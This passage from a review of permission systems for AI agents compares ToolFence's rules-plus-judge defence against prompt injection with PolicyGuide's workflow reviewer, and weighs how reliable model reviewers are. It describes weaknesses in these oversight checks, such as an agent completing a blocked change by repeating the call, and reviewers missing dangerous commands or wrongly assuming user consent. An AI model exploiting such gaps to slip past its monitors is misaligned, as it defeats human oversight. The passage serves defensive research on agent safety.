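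### Filling gaps in the rules

ToolFence's rules decide most calls, and its judge is there for legitimate steps that the rules left out. Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a bill and e-mail the receipt to their accountant, whose address is in their contacts. The model that wrote the permissions for this task forgot the e-mail. The process then goes as follows:

1. The agent proposes the e-mail, and the rules find no permission for it.
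2. ToolFence works out where each argument came from. If a sensitive one, such as the recipient, appears in neither the user's request nor a tool's output, it refuses without consulting the judge.
3. Otherwise it drafts a permission, such as "send an e-mail to an address from the contacts list", and gives this to the judge with the user's request. The draft does not contain the address itself.
4. The judge grants or denies the permission. ToolFence treats an unreadable answer as a denial.
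5. If the judge grants it, the rules still check the actual call. The address must appear in the contacts list, and the permission must have uses left.

The judge cannot approve a particular address, so a mistaken grant does limited harm. However, a grant can cover several calls, and ToolFence can reuse its general form in later sessions, so Li and colleagues instruct the judge to be at least as strict about a grant as about a single call.

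In an early version of their paper, they compared this arrangement with a judge that reviewed every call, using AgentDojo and an agent on Qwen3-max:

| Arrangement | Utility under attack | Attack success | Judge consultations per task | Time, compared with no defence |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 31.9% | 21.2% | None | 1.00× |
| Judge reviews every call | 31.2% | 4.4% | 6.35 | 3.20× |
| Rules only | 25.6% | 0.45% | None | 1.45× |
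| Rules, with judge for missing permissions | 30.4% | 0.18% | 1.84 | 2.78× |
| Full ToolFence | 32.5% | 0.20% | 0.82 | 1.90× |

The judge alone stopped most attacks with almost no loss of utility. Using only the rules stopped nearly all of them, but the agent completed fewer tasks. Letting the judge fill gaps in the rules restored most of the lost task completions without letting more attacks through. The full system also reuses earlier grants and allows simple reads that the user's request supports, so it consults the judge less than once per task on average.

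The final version of the paper reports much higher utility on the same benchmark, so the differences between the rows are more informative than the absolute values. The full system's advantage over a judge that reviews every call was smaller on Agent Security Bench, where attacks succeeded 7.0% of the time with that judge and 5.1% with the full system. Li and colleagues did not test the same judge with and without provenance labels, so their results do not show how much the labels improve its decisions.

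### Following a written procedure

PolicyGuide's reviewer tracks whether the agent has met the preconditions in a company's written policy. Before deployment, a model converts the policy into a workflow, a chart of steps with a condition for completing each one. Software checks that every step is reachable and that every state-changing tool has an authorisation step. Kang and colleagues also checked the workflows by hand but did not edit them.

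For a flight cancellation, the steps might be to identify the customer, look up the booking, check that it qualifies and get the customer's confirmation. Before the agent answers each customer message, the reviewer resumes at the last recorded step and checks the conversation against each condition in turn. Facts must be confirmed by a tool result, and consent must come from the customer's own messages. The reviewer stops at the first unmet condition and tells the agent what to do next. Once all the conditions are met, it enables the cancellation tool. Ordinary software records the current step, so the reviewer does not have to keep track of it.

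Kang and colleagues tested this on τ²-Bench, with GPT 5.4 as both agent and reviewer. They compared it with an unreviewed agent and with PolicyGuard, which reviews only state-changing calls. The table shows the share of tasks that the agent completed in all four attempts:

| | Airline | Retail | Telecom |
|---|---|---|---|
| No reviewer | 46.0% | 59.6% | 19.3% |
| PolicyGuard | 58.0% | 60.5% | 20.2% |
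| PolicyGuide | 62.0% | 61.4% | 61.4% |

The gain in telecom is probably large because about 54% of that policy's requirements specify an order of steps, compared with less than 5% in the other two. An agent helping a customer repair a phone connection may go wrong several steps before it changes anything itself, so a check on state-changing calls comes too late or never happens.

Most of PolicyGuide's advantage came from helping the agent complete permitted changes. It was no better than PolicyGuard at preventing forbidden changes in the airline tests. Of the 24 tasks where the agent had to avoid a forbidden change, it succeeded in all four attempts on 22 (91.7%) with PolicyGuide and on all 24 with PolicyGuard.

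Its gate is also weaker than an enforcement point. When the agent proposes a change that the reviewer has not enabled, the software stops the call and consults the reviewer again. But it then lets all further calls through until the customer's next message, so an agent could ignore the reviewer's advice and complete the change by repeating the call. To guarantee that no change is made without the reviewer's approval, an operator would have to keep blocking the call until the reviewer enabled it.

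### Can a model be trusted to review another?

Critics say that a reviewer model offers no guarantee and shares the weaknesses of the model it reviews. Michael and Roesner add that such reviewers are opaque and give users little control. In Codex, for example, users can only switch the reviewer on or off for all tools in a session, so they cannot leave file edits to the reviewer while personally approving every e-mail.

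Reviewer models missed bad actions in Anthropic's tests and in AmPermBench, and no one has proved a limit on how often this will happen. ToolFence can limit the damage from a mistaken grant only because fixed rules check the call afterwards.

The evidence for shared weaknesses is less clear. In PolicyGuide, the same model caught mistakes as a reviewer that it had made as an agent. On a smaller set of telecom tasks, an agent with the workflow in its instructions completed 32.5% of the tasks in all four attempts. When a separate reviewer followed the workflow, the figure was 67.5%. The reviewer also had stored records and could advise the agent before each reply, so separation may not explain the whole difference. These were ordinary mistakes rather than attacks, and an attack that works on one copy of a model may well work on another. Testing the same agent with reviewers from different model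 families would help settle the question.

Supporters argue that a model can judge what the user intended, which rules cannot, and that it is more consistent than a tired person. In Anthropic's August 2026 experiment, auto mode caught 89% of the planted dangerous commands, compared with 13.6% for the human testers, and its rate did not fall as sessions grew longer. This is good evidence that a model reviewer stays consistent over long sessions, at least when the danger is obvious.

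A reviewer model may give different answers when it sees the same borderline call more than once. Yan had a model classify 20 tools by their effects, ten times each. The model gave the ten clear-cut tools the same labels every time, but its label for the type of action varied for five of the ten difficult ones. It was classifying descriptions of tools rather than reviewing calls, so the result is only indirect evidence about reviewers.

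The claim about intent holds best when the task is clear, as in Yan's user study, where the reviewer flagged every excessive action and only a few necessary ones. Auto mode's reviewer did badly on the ambiguous requests in AmPermBench. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer had identified the danger but wrongly treated the user as having consented. Misjudged intent is therefore a major source of the reviewer's errors, even though judging intent is the main reason to use one.

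A reviewer may be most useful for choosing which calls a person should see. Suppose ten calls in 10,000 are bad. At Anthropic's rates, the reviewer would flag about 48 calls, including eight of the bad ones. A person could examine 48 calls far more carefully than 10,000, but the two bad calls the reviewer missed would go through, and the person might still approve some of the eight it flagged, as many of Yan's participants did.

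The risk also depends on what the operator lets the reviewer decide. A reviewer that can only refuse calls or refer them to a person will raise some false alarms, but the rules still block everything they would have blocked without it. If the reviewer can approve calls, any call it wrongly approves may be carried out. For irreversible payments, an operator can therefore use the reviewer as an additional check while still requiring the user's approval.
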